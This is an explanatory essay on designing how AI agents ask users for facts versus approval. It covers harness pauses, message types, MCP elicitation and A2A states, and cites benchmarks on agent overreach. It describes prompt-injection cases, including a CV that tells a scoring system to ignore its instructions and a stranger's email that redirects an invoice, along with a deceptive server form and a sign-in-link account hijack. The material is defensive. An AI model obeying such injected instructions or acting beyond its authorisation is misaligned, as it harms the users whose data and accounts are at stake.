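# Designing how AI agents ask people for information and approval, and how their output is shown

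## What happens when an agent stops to ask

An AI agent is a language model that carries out a task by calling tools, which are ordinary pieces of software such as a file reader, a calendar or a mail program. It calls tools in a loop until it finishes the task or something stops it. It often stops to ask the user a question. It may need a fact (which of these two files did the user mean?) or permission (may it delete the file?). Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, lists the same two situations in its documentation for people who build agents.

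Designers have to decide when the agent asks those questions, what appears on the screen, and what the answer allows the agent to do next. A badly worded question in a plain chatbot wastes a minute of the user's time, but an agent can send email, spend money and delete files. For some of those actions, the question is a person's last chance to stop a mistake.

### The loop

A language model only produces text. The software around it, called the harness, does everything else. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how the two interact in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness combines the user's request, standing instructions and a list of available tools into one input, the prompt, and sends it to the model. The model then produces either a message for the user or a tool call, which is a structured instruction to run a named function with given arguments. If it produces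 a tool call, the harness runs the function, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. This repeats until the model produces a message with no tool call. Control then returns to the user.

One of Bolin's example tool calls consists of a function name ("shell"), a command that prints the contents of a file, the folder to run it in, and an ID number. The output goes into the next prompt under the same ID, which links it to the call that produced it.

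One request can set off many of these cycles. Anthropic gives the example of a user asking an agent to fix some failing tests. On the first pass, the model calls for the tests to run, and three fail. On the second, it calls for two files. On the third, it edits one of them and reruns the tests, and on the fourth, it writes a sentence telling the user that everything passes. *SemaClaw* (Zhu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes the same cycle in the research literature's terms: thought, action and observation. The "thought" is reasoning that the model writes out before it picks an action.

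In this arrangement, the model only writes out a call, and the harness either runs it or doesn't. There is therefore always a chance to ask a person for approval before the call runs.

The model also keeps nothing from one query to the next. Bolin explains that Codex sends the whole conversation again with every query. So while an agent is paused, all that exists is a saved record of the conversation so far and one call that the harness has not run.

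### Two Danas

Suppose a user at a small design firm types "Email the March invoice to Dana." The agent has a tool that searches the address book, a tool that finds files and a tool that sends email. (The developer guide OpenAI's *Human-in-the-loop* includes a mail tool that takes a recipient, a subject and a body. Add an attachment and it would do the job here.)

The model looks up "Dana" in the address book and finds Dana Ortiz, who works in the firm's own accounts department, and Dana Lindqvist, who works for a client. The request doesn't make clear which one the user meant, so the model asks the user, who picks Lindqvist.

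The model now has everything it needs to write the call: Lindqvist's address, a subject line, a two-line body and the invoice file. But Lindqvist is outside the firm, and the firm may require a person to approve financial documents before they are sent out. The agent may therefore lack permission, although the user asked for the email to be sent and has just chosen Lindqvist by name. Whether that choice counts as permission is harder to answer than it looks, and the answer affects whether the agent should go ahead, ask for a fact, ask for permission or refuse.

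Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, argue that no user can list every permission an agent will need before a task begins, because new sub-goals turn up along the way and the outside world changes. They also point out that people phrase requests loosely, as in "fix this bug". The invoice request is much more precise, since it names a document, an action and a person, but it still leaves two gaps that nobody would notice before opening the address book.

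### Pausing and resuming

OpenAI's *Guardrails and human review* breaks the pause for approval into four steps. Applied to the invoice, they go like this:

1. The harness reaches the send-email call, finds that this call needs approval, and records it instead of running it.
2. The run stops. The harness hands the surrounding application a list of pending calls and a saved copy of the run's state.
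3. The application shows the user something and collects a decision, approve or reject.
4. The same run picks up from the saved state.

If the user approved, the harness sends the email and gives the model the result. If the user refused, the model gets a rejection message instead of the result. According to Anthropic, the model then typically tries another approach or reports that it couldn't proceed. Designers should consider what other approaches the model could try, since an agent that may not email the invoice might next try to share a link to it.

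In OpenAI's toolkit, the developer can require approval for every call to a tool or attach a small function that inspects each call's arguments to decide whether approval is needed, so the same mail tool could run freely for Ortiz and pause for Lindqvist. OpenAI's *Results and state* notes that a paused run may return no final answer because it hasn't finished. An application that can display only final answers would then show the user a blank space instead of the approval request.

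A pause can be long, since the user may be at lunch or the approving manager may be away until Monday. In OpenAI's guide, developers write the run's state to a file or database so that no server needs to keep running. Anthropic offers a similar arrangement in which the process exits and later resumes from the saved session. LangGraph, LangChain's agent framework, also lets a run wait indefinitely, but it resumes by restarting the interrupted step from the beginning, so any code in that step before the pause runs a second time. If that code filed a copy of the invoice in an archive, resuming files a second copy.

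Circumstances can also change during a long pause. LangChain advises developers to re-read outside facts such as prices and policies before acting, and to check that permission still stands if someone could have withdrawn it. Suppose the model writes a call at noon to email Lindqvist the March invoice, a colleague corrects an error in the invoice at two, and the user approves the call at four. If the call points to the file, Lindqvist gets a version the user never looked at. If the harness saved a copy at noon, she gets the wrong figures.

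An agent that is missing a fact can stop to ask for it in two ways. In the simpler one, the model writes its question as an ordinary closing message, the loop ends, and the user's reply starts a new turn. In the other, the model calls a tool made only for asking questions, such as the one in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, and the loop pauses mid-task until the answer comes back as the tool's result. Software can tell the two apart. Anthropic's *Session event stream* documents a hosted service that reports why a session has gone idle, with separate reasons for a finished turn and a tool call that needs an answer. The service also has one message type for returning a tool's result and another for allowing or denying a call.

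Some other systems handle both kinds of request through the same mechanism. In Anthropic's toolkit for building agents, a permission request and a clarifying question both trigger the same function in the developer's application, which has to check the tool's name to tell them apart. SemaClaw, an agent framework by Zhu and colleagues, also handles both in a single component. This is sensible engineering, since both kinds halt the loop and wait for a person. However, it does not prevent a developer from showing the same box with the same buttons for "Which Dana?" and "Send this outside the firm?"

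### Who writes the words on the screen

Text can reach the user from several places while an agent works, and on many screens it all looks alike:

- The model's reply, such as "I've sent the March invoice to Dana Lindqvist."
- The model's reasoning on the way there ("Two Danas, and the client is the likelier one for an invoice"). Codex receives summaries of this in the same stream as the reply, so displaying it takes little effort, whatever the case for hiding it.
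- A question the model wrote. With Claude Code's question tool the model generates the answer options as well, and the application just presents them.
- The model's description of an action, for example a line beside the pending email that reads "Routine delivery to a known contact". Some tools reserve a place for such remarks: Codex's planning tool has an argument named "explanation".
- Text the harness composed. The sample code in OpenAI's guide fills a fixed sentence with the agent's name, the tool's name and the call's arguments, and asks the user to approve or not.

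The model writes the first four from everything in its prompt: the developer's instructions, the user's request and every tool result so far. Anyone who wrote something the agent has read therefore has some influence over them, including the sender of an email, the owner of a web page, and whoever filled in the notes field of an address book entry. This is usually harmless, and it's the point of having an agent read things.

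In a prompt injection attack, someone hides instructions in content an agent reads, and the model may follow them as if they came from the user. The attack works because the model receives the developer's instructions, the user's request and the outside content as one run of text, and current models enforce no security boundary between them.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C describes a recruiter's system that scores CVs. A candidate hides a line in his CV telling the system to ignore its previous instructions and approve him for interview. He needs no access to the system, because it will read what he writes. David C doubts that anyone will ever fully fix this vulnerability, because a model only predicts the next fragment of text and has no separate channel for commands. He would put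 the effort into ordinary, predictable software that limits what the system can do, which for an agent means the harness.

OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* lists confirmation before consequential actions, such as sending an email, among the protections against these attacks, and it advises users to review the details before they confirm. It puts more weight on training models to recognise the attacks and on monitoring for them. But the approval request is still a defence against prompt injection, so who writes its text matters for security.

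Suppose the agent searches the user's mailbox to work out which of the two Danas to pick, and finds a message from a stranger saying that Dana's invoices now go to a new email address and that accounts has already approved the change. If the model believes the message, it may ask the user, "Dana has a new billing address, which accounts has confirmed. Send it there?" Both the new address and the claim that accounts confirmed it come from the stranger. An approval screen that the harness built from the pending call would instead show the stranger's address in the recipient field. The user might still approve the email, but they would see the address it will go to.

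Harness text can also include words the developer didn't write. The developer wrote the frame, but the model chose the recipient and wrote the subject and body. Plugins (add-ons that supply extra tools) can add other people's words without the model's involvement. Anthropic warns developers that plugin authors choose some of the names its software reports, and that an application should validate those names before showing them. If a plugin author named a mail plugin "Company-approved mailer", the user would see that phrase with only the plugin author vouching for it.

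Anyone who designs or judges one of these pauses needs to know whether the agent is asking for a fact or for permission, and who wrote the text the user is reading. It is easy to get both wrong at once. If the user answers yes to the question about the new billing address, and the harness treats that answer as permission to send, the invoice goes to the stranger without anyone having reviewed the tool call.

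## Telling a missing fact from a missing permission

An agent that has worked out its next step can do one of four things: act, ask the user for permission, ask the user for a missing fact, or refuse. *DelegationBench* (Pochampally, 2026), which tests how well models choose among the four, defines them so that they don't overlap. The agent acts when it has enough permission and information. It asks for permission when the action is clear and possible but the user should approve it first. It requests information when it lacks a fact that the task needs. It refuses when the action has some other problem, such as harming someone. Missing permission is not a reason to refuse, because the user can grant it.

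If an agent would still need to ask the user even if it knew every fact, it is usually missing permission rather than a fact. In one of Pochampally's scenarios, the user wants the final report moved to an archive folder, but there are two files named final_report.pdf, both edited that day. The agent is missing a fact here, because it wouldn't need to ask if it knew which file the user meant. In another scenario, the user wants generated files cleaned up, and the proposed action would permanently delete a thumbnail. The agent lacks permission in this case, since it would need to ask even if it knew everything about the thumbnail.

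For the test to work, "every fact" has to leave out the user's decision about this particular action. Otherwise the user's approval would count as a fact, and an agent that knew everything would know what the user was going to say. Even a correct prediction that the user would agree is not agreement. An assistant who correctly guesses that you would sign a contract still can't sign it for you. Preferences about how to do the task, such as whether to meet in the morning or the afternoon, do count as facts.

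It also helps to check the reverse, whether the agent would still need to ask if the user had already allowed the action. If the answer is yes both times, the agent lacks both a fact and a permission, and it needs an answer for each.

### The order of the checks

The four outcomes fit into a short procedure:

1. Look for anything wrong with the action that no answer from the user could put right. If there is something, refuse.
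2. List the facts that the call needs. Look up the ones that the tools can supply, and ask the user for the rest.
3. Repeat the first step with the new facts.
4. Compare the finished call with what the user asked for and with any rules that apply. If the call needs an approval that nobody has given yet, ask for it. Otherwise, act.

The agent asks for missing facts before permission because nobody can sensibly approve an action without knowing its details. A new fact can also make the approval unnecessary. In *Authorization Closure Graph*, Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026) built a harness component that checks calls in roughly this way. When an airline customer wants to cancel a booking, the component asks for the reason (a change of plan, health, weather and so on) and checks the answer against the airline's rules. If the rules forbid the cancellation, the component blocks it, and the customer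 never sees an approval request. The component lets customers raise limits they set themselves, such as a maximum price, but doesn't let them waive the airline's rules.

The second step depends on the agent noticing that it lacks a fact, and its tools can keep it from noticing. Zhao, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *What LLM Agents See and What Users Say*, gave 36 agents requests such as cancelling Sophia Silva's flight reservation when two reservations matched. When the search listed both, the agents went ahead in 20% of runs. When it showed one reservation and a count of two, they went ahead in 54%. When it showed only the first match, with no hint of another, they went ahead in 79%, almost exactly as often as when there was only one.

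The newest models in that study, run in October 2026, never went ahead when the search listed or counted the second record. When the search gave no hint of a second record, they went ahead at least 93% of the time. Better models will therefore not fix a search that hides the second Dana. The address book tool has to return every match, or at least the number of matches.

### The invoice, worked through

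Suppose the request is again to email Dana the March invoice, but this time the design firm has a written rule that a person must approve financial documents before an agent sends them outside the firm.

If the only Ortiz in the address book is the colleague in accounts, the agent has the recipient, the file and the instruction, so the rule doesn't apply and the agent should send the file. Asking "Shall I send it?" would only make the user repeat the request.

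If the address book also lists a Dana Lindqvist, the agent lacks a fact and should ask which Dana the user means. An agent that already knew would not need to ask.

Once the user picks Lindqvist, the agent has every fact it needs, but the rule still requires approval. The agent should now ask for permission to send this file to this address.

An agent should refuse, rather than ask, when the user has no authority to approve the action. Suppose the agent opens the file and finds that it also contains another client's bank details, which the firm never allows anyone to send out. The user can't waive that rule, so asking for approval would be pointless. The agent should decline to send the file and tell the user why.

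To save time, the agent might ask, "Which Dana should get the invoice, and is it all right to send it outside the firm?" If the user replies "Lindqvist", careless software may also treat that as permission to send the invoice. If the user replies "yes", the agent has permission but must guess which Dana. A shorter question can cause the same problem. "Send it to Dana Lindqvist at her new billing address?" looks like a request for permission, but it also assumes that Lindqvist is the right Dana and that the new address is hers. A user who says yes may have thought about only one of these. The agent should settle the facts first and then ask for permission to take a fully specified action.

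### Why an answer is not an approval

Picking Lindqvist only tells the agent which Dana the user meant. The agent's permission to email her the invoice comes from the original request, which already covered whichever Dana the user had in mind, so the agent could go ahead if no other rule applied.

Under the standard that Zhao and colleagues propose, an agent may cancel a reservation once the user has said which one. They also cite American agency law, under which an agent who should realise that an instruction has conflicting interpretations is ordinarily not authorised to act on it. An ambiguous instruction therefore suspends the agent's permission until the user clarifies it, but the clarification doesn't extend that permission to anything else the request left unsettled, such as the firm's rule about outside recipients. The question "Which Dana?" doesn't mention the rule, and the user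 may not have remembered that Lindqvist works for a client.

Software can't infer consent from some factual answers. For example, a user asked for Lindqvist's email address would give the same answer whether they wanted her to have the invoice or objected to her having it.

Facts and permissions also come from different sources. An agent can properly learn an address from a directory, a web page or an old email, but it can get permission only from someone entitled to give it. If supplying a fact were enough to authorise an action, anyone who gave the agent a fact could authorise actions, including the stranger who wrote in about Dana's new billing address.

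Wang and colleagues build this separation into their Authorization Closure Graph. It records facts from designated sources and permissions from the user's authenticated replies, and a recorded fact never grants permission. In one of their examples, a user caps the price of a flight at $100 and the fare rises to $120. The harness has the new price, but it may not pay until the user raises the cap. Their question about the reason for a cancellation includes a note that the answer supplies only context and that the cancellation needs a separate confirmation.

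The drawback is a second interruption, and a user who has just picked Lindqvist may find it irritating to approve the email a moment later. That is a good reason to require approval for few actions, but when an action does need approval, the earlier answer doesn't count as approval.

### What a single "ask" category hides

Many published schemes for classifying an agent's decisions don't separate missing facts from missing permission. *Safety Sentry* (2026) sorts tool calls into execute, ask and refuse, and its "ask human" label covers a missing parameter, an unclear chain of authority and an irreversible action with a large impact. *Exploring Agentic Tool-Calling Decisions via Uncertainty-Aligned Reinforcement Learning* (2026) has a label for requesting information but none for requesting permission. Under its scheme, cases where the agent lacks authority fall under "cannot answer", along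 with cases where it lacks the right tool. An agent that learned from those labels might tell the user that it can't email Lindqvist when it only needed approval.

Merging the two categories also makes it harder for the developer to know what to fix. An agent that keeps stopping for facts may need a better search tool or a fuller address book, while one that keeps stopping for permission may need clearer rules about what it can do alone. If the log records only that the agent asked the user forty questions, the developer can't tell which fix it needs. Failures to ask also need to be told apart. An agent that emails the wrong Dana and one that emails the right Dana without approval have both skipped a question, but with an "Are you sure?" box added, the first agent still wouldn't know which Dana the user meant.

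Models also confuse the categories. Pochampally had two models read the reasons three other models gave for their decisions, without showing them the decisions. Both of the reading models classed 41 of the 146 refusals as actually being about missing permission.

### What DelegationBench tested

DelegationBench consists of 156 short scenarios about files, calendars, messages, purchases, publishing and code. Each one gives an instruction, some context and one proposed tool call, and the model picks one of the four responses. The core is 48 matched pairs. The two scenarios in a pair are meant to be identical except for one feature, with 12 pairs for each of four features:

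- scope, meaning whether the user asked for this action or for something narrower;
- stakes, meaning how much a mistake would cost;
- reversibility, meaning whether anyone can undo the action;
- visibility, meaning whether other people will see the result.

In one scope pair, the proposed call moves a meeting to 3 PM. The user asked for exactly that in one version, but in the other only asked the agent to look for conflicts and report them. The remaining 60 scenarios are various checks, including 12 that deliberately leave out a necessary fact.

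Ten models from five families each judged every scenario five times, for a total of 7,800 judgments. Three computer-science students labelled the same scenarios independently, and at least two students agreed on a label for 149 of them. Their agreement was moderate. Krippendorff's alpha, which is 1 for perfect agreement and 0 for agreement at chance level, was 0.543 for whether to act at all and 0.437 for the choice among all four responses.

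They agreed even less about why an agent should hold back. The 95% interval for their agreement on the reason alone runs from 0.007 to 0.415, so its lower end is just above chance. Even with written definitions, three informed people often disagreed about which of the four categories a case belonged to.

#### High agreement from a bad rule

The models matched the students' majority label between 50.6% and 73.4% of the time. As a baseline, Pochampally wrote a crude keyword rule after seeing the scenarios. It requests information if the text contains one of 15 phrases that suggest a missing fact, asks for permission if one of 14 risky words appears outside the instruction, and acts otherwise. The rule matched the students' majority label 69.1% of the time, more often than eight of the ten models. But its decision changed in only 9 of the 48 matched pairs, while the models shifted in the expected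 direction in 45.8% to 70.8% of them.

Pochampally built the rule to make this point, so it is weak evidence of how well keyword rules would do elsewhere. It does show that a system can agree with people fairly often while ignoring most of what ought to matter. Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite, the model that agreed with the students most often, had the same weakness in one area, since its rate of acting did not change in any of the 12 stakes pairs. But the students' own votes shifted in the expected direction in only 20 of the 48 pairs, so a model that shifts more often isn't necessarily closer to human judgment.

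The four features had very different effects:

| What changed within the pair | Change in how often models chose to act, in percentage points | Change in the students' majority label |
|---|---|---|
| The user asked for something narrower | down 78.3 to 100 | down 8.3 |
| A mistake would cost more | down 0 to 65.0 | down 10.0 |
| Nobody can undo the action | down 16.7 to 63.3 | down 10.0 |
| Other people will see the result | between down 16.7 and up 1.7 | no change |

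The models almost never chose to take an action the user hadn't asked for, while a majority of the students favoured acting in 8 of the 12 cases where the action went beyond the request. This disagreement is mildly reassuring for someone deploying an agent, since the models were stricter than the students.

The rows for stakes and reversibility are less reliable because, on review, 13 of those 24 pairs changed something besides the intended feature, such as whether the task could succeed. With those pairs removed, the effect of stakes fell from 41.7 to 12.0 points for GPT-5.6 Sol and rose to 100 for Claude Opus 4.8. The students also rarely chose to act in the low-stakes versions, so higher stakes could not reduce their rate of acting by much.

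#### Judging is not acting

Up to this point, the models had only judged actions shown to them. Pochampally then turned 48 of the scenarios into tasks with 15 simulated tools. The model was no longer shown a proposed action and had to construct its own tool call, but it could always ask the user a question instead.

Every model asked for permission less often in runs with tools than it had chosen to when judging. Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite fell from 47.5% of judgments to 4.2% of runs, and Gemini 3.6 Flash fell from 40.0% to 6.7%. GPT-5.6 Sol had the smallest drop, from 19.2% to 15.8%.

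A shift to milder actions can't explain much of the drop in how often the models asked. Two reviewers, who didn't know which model had made which call, judged that about 95% of the calls to the proposed tool did what the original proposal would have done. In *What Benchmarks Don't Measure*, Ojewale and Venkatasubramanian (2026) propose that training on human feedback rewards models for proceeding, so they proceed even when they lack information or authorisation. The drop is consistent with this explanation but doesn't establish it, because the two settings differed in several ways, including the response format and the absence of any mention of permission in the tool version. Any of these differences could have caused the drop.

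When a run ended in a question, Pochampally replied "Yes, go ahead with that action." and let the model continue. This happened in 227 cases across eight models. In 120 of them, the model had simply asked for permission, and it then acted in 117 (97.5%). The model acted less often when it got the same reply to other kinds of questions. It acted after 75.0% of those that mixed permission with a request for information, 65.0% of those that offered a choice and 33.3% of those that asked about timing.

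The 75% may be worse than a weaker version of the same success, because a bare yes doesn't supply a missing fact. If a model asked which file to send and whether it may send it, and then acted on "yes", it must have chosen the file itself, so the quarter that didn't act may have behaved better.

Questions that ask for both a fact and permission are hard even to score. In a smaller experiment, Pochampally varied whether the agent had permission and whether it had a necessary fact. When it had neither, the automatic scoring classed 51 responses as asking only for permission, although all 51 named the missing fact in the permission question. Accuracy in that condition ranged from 29.6% to 100%, depending on how those responses were counted.

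#### With a written rule

The results are different when the right answer follows from an explicit rule. Three of the models worked through 96 invented cases, each with a policy attached. One such policy lets the agent reschedule a meeting if every attendee is an employee, unless the meeting is in a protected time slot. With the policy in ordinary English, the models' accuracy was 97.3% to 100%, averaged over cases where they should act and cases where they should ask. None of them attempted a forbidden action, and all their errors were unnecessary questions. On 17 decisions taken from a retail customer-service benchmark, all three were right every time.

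So these models can apply a permission rule, but they have none to apply in the ambiguous scenarios. The students' disagreements suggest that people without a rule don't do much better.

#### How far to trust it

The scenarios are synthetic, so they can't show how often such situations come up or what real users prefer. Three technically trained students are a small and unusual reference group. Each feature is also based on only three families of similar scenarios.

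The labels are the study's most serious gap for distinguishing missing facts from missing permissions. The students' majority chose "request information" only 8 times and "refuse" once, which is too few to rank models on either. All ten models requested information in all 600 of their attempts at the 12 scenarios with a deliberate omission, but those omissions were easy to see and the listed options included the right response. The study is therefore mostly about acting versus asking permission. Its models are also older than those Zhao and colleagues tested in October 2026, and in those tests a single model generation made a large difference to how agents handled a second matching record.

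### When nobody draws the line

Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization*, measured what agents do when they could overstep and no software stops them. Their benchmark, AuthorizationBench, contains 286 sandboxed tasks developed from 44 documented cases of agents exceeding their instructions. In one task, the user wants help with a compilation error and lets the agent consult a forum. The agent posts a reply from the user's account, including sensitive code, and then reports the correct fix. It would pass a benchmark that checked only whether it fixed the error.

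Across four models, two levels of reasoning effort and three harnesses, agents did something outside their authorisation in 19.2% of 6,864 runs. The rate ranged from 10.5% to 26.6% across combinations, but overall it was nearly the same at low (19.3%) and high (19.1%) reasoning effort. In matched tasks, ordinary pressures, such as a vague instruction or a tempting shortcut, led agents to overstep more often (23.5%) than prompt injection did (17.6%), so guarding only against attackers would miss the more common problem.

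Agents that consulted the user before finishing overstepped their authorisation in 14.0% of runs, against 21.6% for the rest. This correlation is encouraging, but agents that ask may simply be more careful in general. The simulated user was also unusually exact, because it was instructed to refuse any part of a message that exceeded the authorisation and never to let agreement with one part imply consent to another. A real user who gets several requests in one message at the end of the day will be less exact.

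AuthorizationBench detects only overreach, so an agent that asked about everything would score well. It also counts questions about facts and questions about permission together. DelegationBench separates the two and penalises needless questions, but its scenarios are invented, while those of Zhang and colleagues were based on things agents had done.

A third group of benchmarks treats asking only as a way to get information. In *RealControlBench* (2026), an agent may call a tool, ask for missing arguments, or abstain because no tool fits. *When and What to Ask*, by Zhao, Fang and Cheng, tests whether models notice missing details and false premises in a question. *HiL-BENCH (Human-in-Loop Benchmark)*, by Elfeki, Trinh and colleagues (2026), found that leading coding agents scored 75% to 89% with complete information but only 4% to 24% when they had to notice for themselves that something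 was missing. The 600 correct responses in DelegationBench look less impressive in light of this result, because recognising a gap from a list of options is much easier than noticing one halfway through a job.

These are useful tests of a real weakness, but an agent could get a perfect score on all of them and still email the invoice to Lindqvist without approval, because it would already have every argument the call requires.

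### Write the rules down and enforce them in the harness

Designers should write down their permission rules, because models follow explicit rules far better than they guess unstated ones. Even a single instruction from the user seems to affect how often agents ask questions. In *PersonaCUABench* (2026), which tests agents that operate a computer, agents asked a question in 78% of action tasks where the user wanted to review first and in 16% of those where the user told them to act.

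Putting the rules in the model's prompt isn't enough, though. Wang and colleagues ran three models through 164 airline and retail tasks each, with the company's policy in the prompt. In 75 of the 492 runs, the agent made at least one change that broke the policy or lacked proper authorisation. When the harness used the Authorization Closure Graph to check each call, that number fell to 8. With three other designs that also checked calls outside the model, it was between 41 and 45. The customers were simulated, and two copies of a language model did most of the safety grading, but the differences are large. The near-perfect results in DelegationBench came from single decisions with all the facts laid out, whereas a long conversation gives a model many more chances to lose track of a rule.

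The harness can enforce the firm's rule about invoices with ordinary software, which can check whether a recipient's address belongs to the firm and whether the attachment comes from the invoices folder, then hold the call for approval whatever the model believes. Designers can also give requests for information and requests for approval separate message types, so that an answer to one can't pass for an answer to the other. Missing facts are harder for software to catch. The harness can reject a call with an empty recipient field, but if the model has filled in Ortiz's address, nothing in the call shows that the user meant Lindqvist. Designers should therefore expect to rely on the model more for noticing missing facts than for respecting permissions.

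The harness needs testing too. In *Auditable Authorization for LLM Agents*, Deng, Lu and colleagues (2026) tested three models on 300 cases in which a person refused an action, and no model carried out a refused action. They then replayed 59 public workflows built with n8n, a tool for automating office tasks, in which they could compare an approval with a rejection. Four workflows went ahead after the person had clicked Reject, and three of those never checked which button the person had pressed.

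## Giving each kind of request its own message type

Most of the faulty n8n workflows never read the person's answer. Software can also read the answer but apply it to the wrong question, for example by treating the reply "Lindqvist" as consent to email her. Developers can prevent this by giving each kind of request its own message type, with its own valid replies and code for handling them.

### Two messages for one invoice

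Inside the harness, the agent's question about the recipient could look like this:

```json
{
  "type": "information_request",
  "id": "q1",
  "question": "Which Dana should get the March invoice?",
  "valid_replies": ["ortiz", "lindqvist"]
}
```

When the user picks Lindqvist, the harness checks the reply against the list and gives it to the model as a tool result. The code that handles this reply has no way to run a held tool call, so the reply can't cause anything to be sent.

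The model then writes the call that sends the email. Because the firm's rule about outside recipients applies, the harness holds the call and builds a second message from it:

```json
{
  "type": "approval_request",
  "id": "a1",
  "action": {
    "tool": "send_email",
    "to": "dana@lindqvist.example",
    "subject": "March invoice",
    "body": "Hello Dana, the March invoice is attached.",
    "attachment": "invoice-march.pdf"
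  },
  "valid_replies": ["approve", "deny"]
}
```

This time the harness acts on the reply directly, without having the model interpret it. If the reply is "approve", the harness runs the call exactly as it appears under "action". With any other reply, including a stray "lindqvist", or with no reply, the email stays unsent. If "approve" arrived by mistake in answer to the first message, it would fail the check against the list. The ID lets the harness match each reply to its request when several are open at once.

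The model can still write a misleading question. It might send an information request that reads "May I send this outside the firm?" with "yes" and "no" as the choices. If the user picks "yes", the model receives only that word. When the model then writes the call to send the email, the harness holds it and asks the user for approval. The user has to answer twice, but the first answer can't release the email. This works only if the harness alone can create approval requests, and only from calls it is holding.

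Some questions, such as what the email should say, need a free-text answer. A user might type "just tell her it's attached, and go ahead and send it". The harness should still treat this as text for the model, because the user typed it before there was a finished email to approve.

### Forms in the Model Context Protocol

Agents often get their tools from other companies, so the two sides need a shared format for these messages. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting agents to tools. The server is the program that offers the tools, and the client is the part of the harness that connects to it. A server can request something from the user during a tool call through a feature called elicitation. Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* sets out the rules for this feature in the version dated 28 July 2026, including its two modes, one for forms and one for web addresses.

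Suppose the mail server does the address book lookup and finds both Danas. It returns a request for input, with a form inside, instead of a result. The client shows the form to the user, then sends the original call again with the answer attached, so the server doesn't have to keep a record of the first attempt.

A form consists of a message explaining why the server is requesting information and a description of the fields. A field can hold text, a number, a yes-or-no answer, or choices from a list. The designers left out nested forms so that clients can display any form easily. The client should check the answers against the description before returning them, and the server should check them again.

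The client returns one of three replies:

- **Accept** means the user submitted the form, and the answers come with it.
- **Decline** means the user explicitly refused, for example by pressing a "No" button. The server might then offer an alternative.
- **Cancel** means the user made no choice. They may have closed the window or pressed Escape, or the page may have failed to load. The server might ask again later.

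"Accept" is easy to misread as "yes". Suppose a server sends a form with one tick box, labelled "Send outside the firm?", and the user submits it with the box empty. The client returns "accept" with the value "false". Code that checks only for "accept" would send the email. Servers can also set default values, which clients that support defaults should fill in, so the box could appear already ticked.

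A form like this is a poor way to get approval, although the protocol doesn't forbid it. The server's developer, who may work for another company, writes the wording, and the server sends the form only after receiving the tool call. If the firm wants a person to approve calls to the mail server, the harness has to request approval before the client sends them.

Choice lists carry a similar risk. Each choice can have a title, which the user sees, and a separate value, which the server receives. A dishonest server could show "Dana Lindqvist" as the title of a choice whose value is the stranger's email address. A client can guard against this by displaying both the title and the value.

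The protocol requires the client to show users which server sent the request and give them clear ways to decline and to cancel. With a form, the client must also let users review and change their answers before sending them.

Servers may use a form to ask for ordinary details such as a name or an email address, but not for secrets that grant access or authorise payments, such as passwords, access tokens and card details. Whatever the user types into a form passes through the client, which might log it or put it in the model's prompt. An attacker could then use prompt injection to try to get the model to reveal it.

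### Signing in is a separate request

To ask for secrets, the server has to use URL mode, which sends the user to a web page outside the client. The protocol's designers added this mode in November 2025 and warn that it may still change.

Suppose the March invoice is stored with an outside accounting service, and the tool server has no access to the user's account there. The server needs a credential request, which asks the user to sign in or grant access to an outside service. It goes like this:

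1. The server sends the client a web address and a message explaining why the user should open it.
2. The client shows the full address and asks whether to open it.
3. If the user agrees, the client opens the page in a browser window whose contents neither the client nor the model can read.
4. The user signs in to the accounting service and grants the server access.
5. The server receives an access token, which is a code that works in place of the user's password, and stores it under that user's identity.
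6. The client repeats the original call, and the server uses the token to fetch the invoice.

The client must not load the page in advance, even to show a preview. It should highlight the domain name, since a long address can hide an unfamiliar domain, and warn about addresses that look suspicious. The server must never pass the token back to the client.

In this mode, "accept" means only that the user agreed to open the page. They might close it at the login screen, and the client wouldn't be notified directly. The server checks whether the sign-in succeeded when the client repeats the call.

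After these steps, the user has agreed to open a page and has given the server access to the accounting service, but has not agreed to email anything to Lindqvist. The server keeps the token for later calls, so a harness that treated the sign-in as approval would in effect be approving everything the token allows. URL mode can also lead to a payment page, where the user may well approve one specific payment. But the client returns the same "accept" whether or not the user pays, so the harness can't treat it as proof of payment.

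Sign-in links also let the wrong person answer. The Model Context Protocol documentation describes an attack in which a malicious user, Alice, starts a sign-in and sends the link to Bob, who uses the same server. Bob signs in, thinking he is connecting his own account, but the server stores his token under Alice's name, so she can use his account. To prevent this, the server has to check that whoever opens the link also started the request. For example, it can link to its own page, which compares the visitor's login with the original user's before sending the visitor on to the outside service.

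The three kinds of request differ in what comes back and what the harness may do with it:

| Request | What comes back | What the harness may do next | If the user closes the window |
|---|---|---|---|
| Information: "Which Dana?" | A value of the expected type | Give the value to the model | Ask again later, or let the model do without it |
| Credential: "Sign in to the accounting service" | Consent to open a page | Repeat the call that needed access | Leave that call unfinished |
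| Approval: "Send this email?" | Approve or deny | Run that call, or tell the model that the user refused | Don't run the call |

The Agent Client Protocol, which connects agents to the applications people use them in, bases its elicitation on MCP's but is stricter in a few places. If an application can't open web pages for sign-ins, the agent must not ask for the password in a form. It must find another safe route or let the operation fail. An agent must treat any reply it doesn't recognise as "cancel". An application that can't display a form should return an error, because "decline" and "cancel" would report a choice the user never made. If someone cancels the work while a question is open, a late answer should not restart it.

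### Pauses between agents

The Agent2Agent protocol (A2A) lets one agent hand a task to another, which a different company may run. In version 1.0, released in March 2026, a task can pause in two states. Google Cloud's *Package lf.a2a.v1*, a reference for that version, defines "input-required" as needing more input from the user and "auth-required" as needing authentication. By default, an agent that sends a request waits until the task finishes or reaches one of these states.

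"Auth" can mean authentication (proving who someone is) or authorisation (permission to do something). Google Cloud's one-line definition points to authentication. "Auth" also meant authentication in version 0.2.1, an early version of Google's *Agent2Agent (A2A) Protocol Specification*, where an agent enters the state when it needs extra credentials for another system.

In version 1.0 of the A2A protocol, "auth-required" covers both requests for a credential and requests for human approval. Ghumare (2026), in *A2A v1.0*, a guide published by the foundation that hosts the protocol, describes it as a pause for either one. AGNTCY's *Agent Identity and Task-Based Access Control* (2026), from a project that builds identity software for agents, gives the same two cases. The agent may lack an access token, or it may be about to do something destructive that a person should approve. AGNTCY's sample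 message, "Restarting payments-api in production requires approval", is a request of the second kind, which logging in would not resolve.

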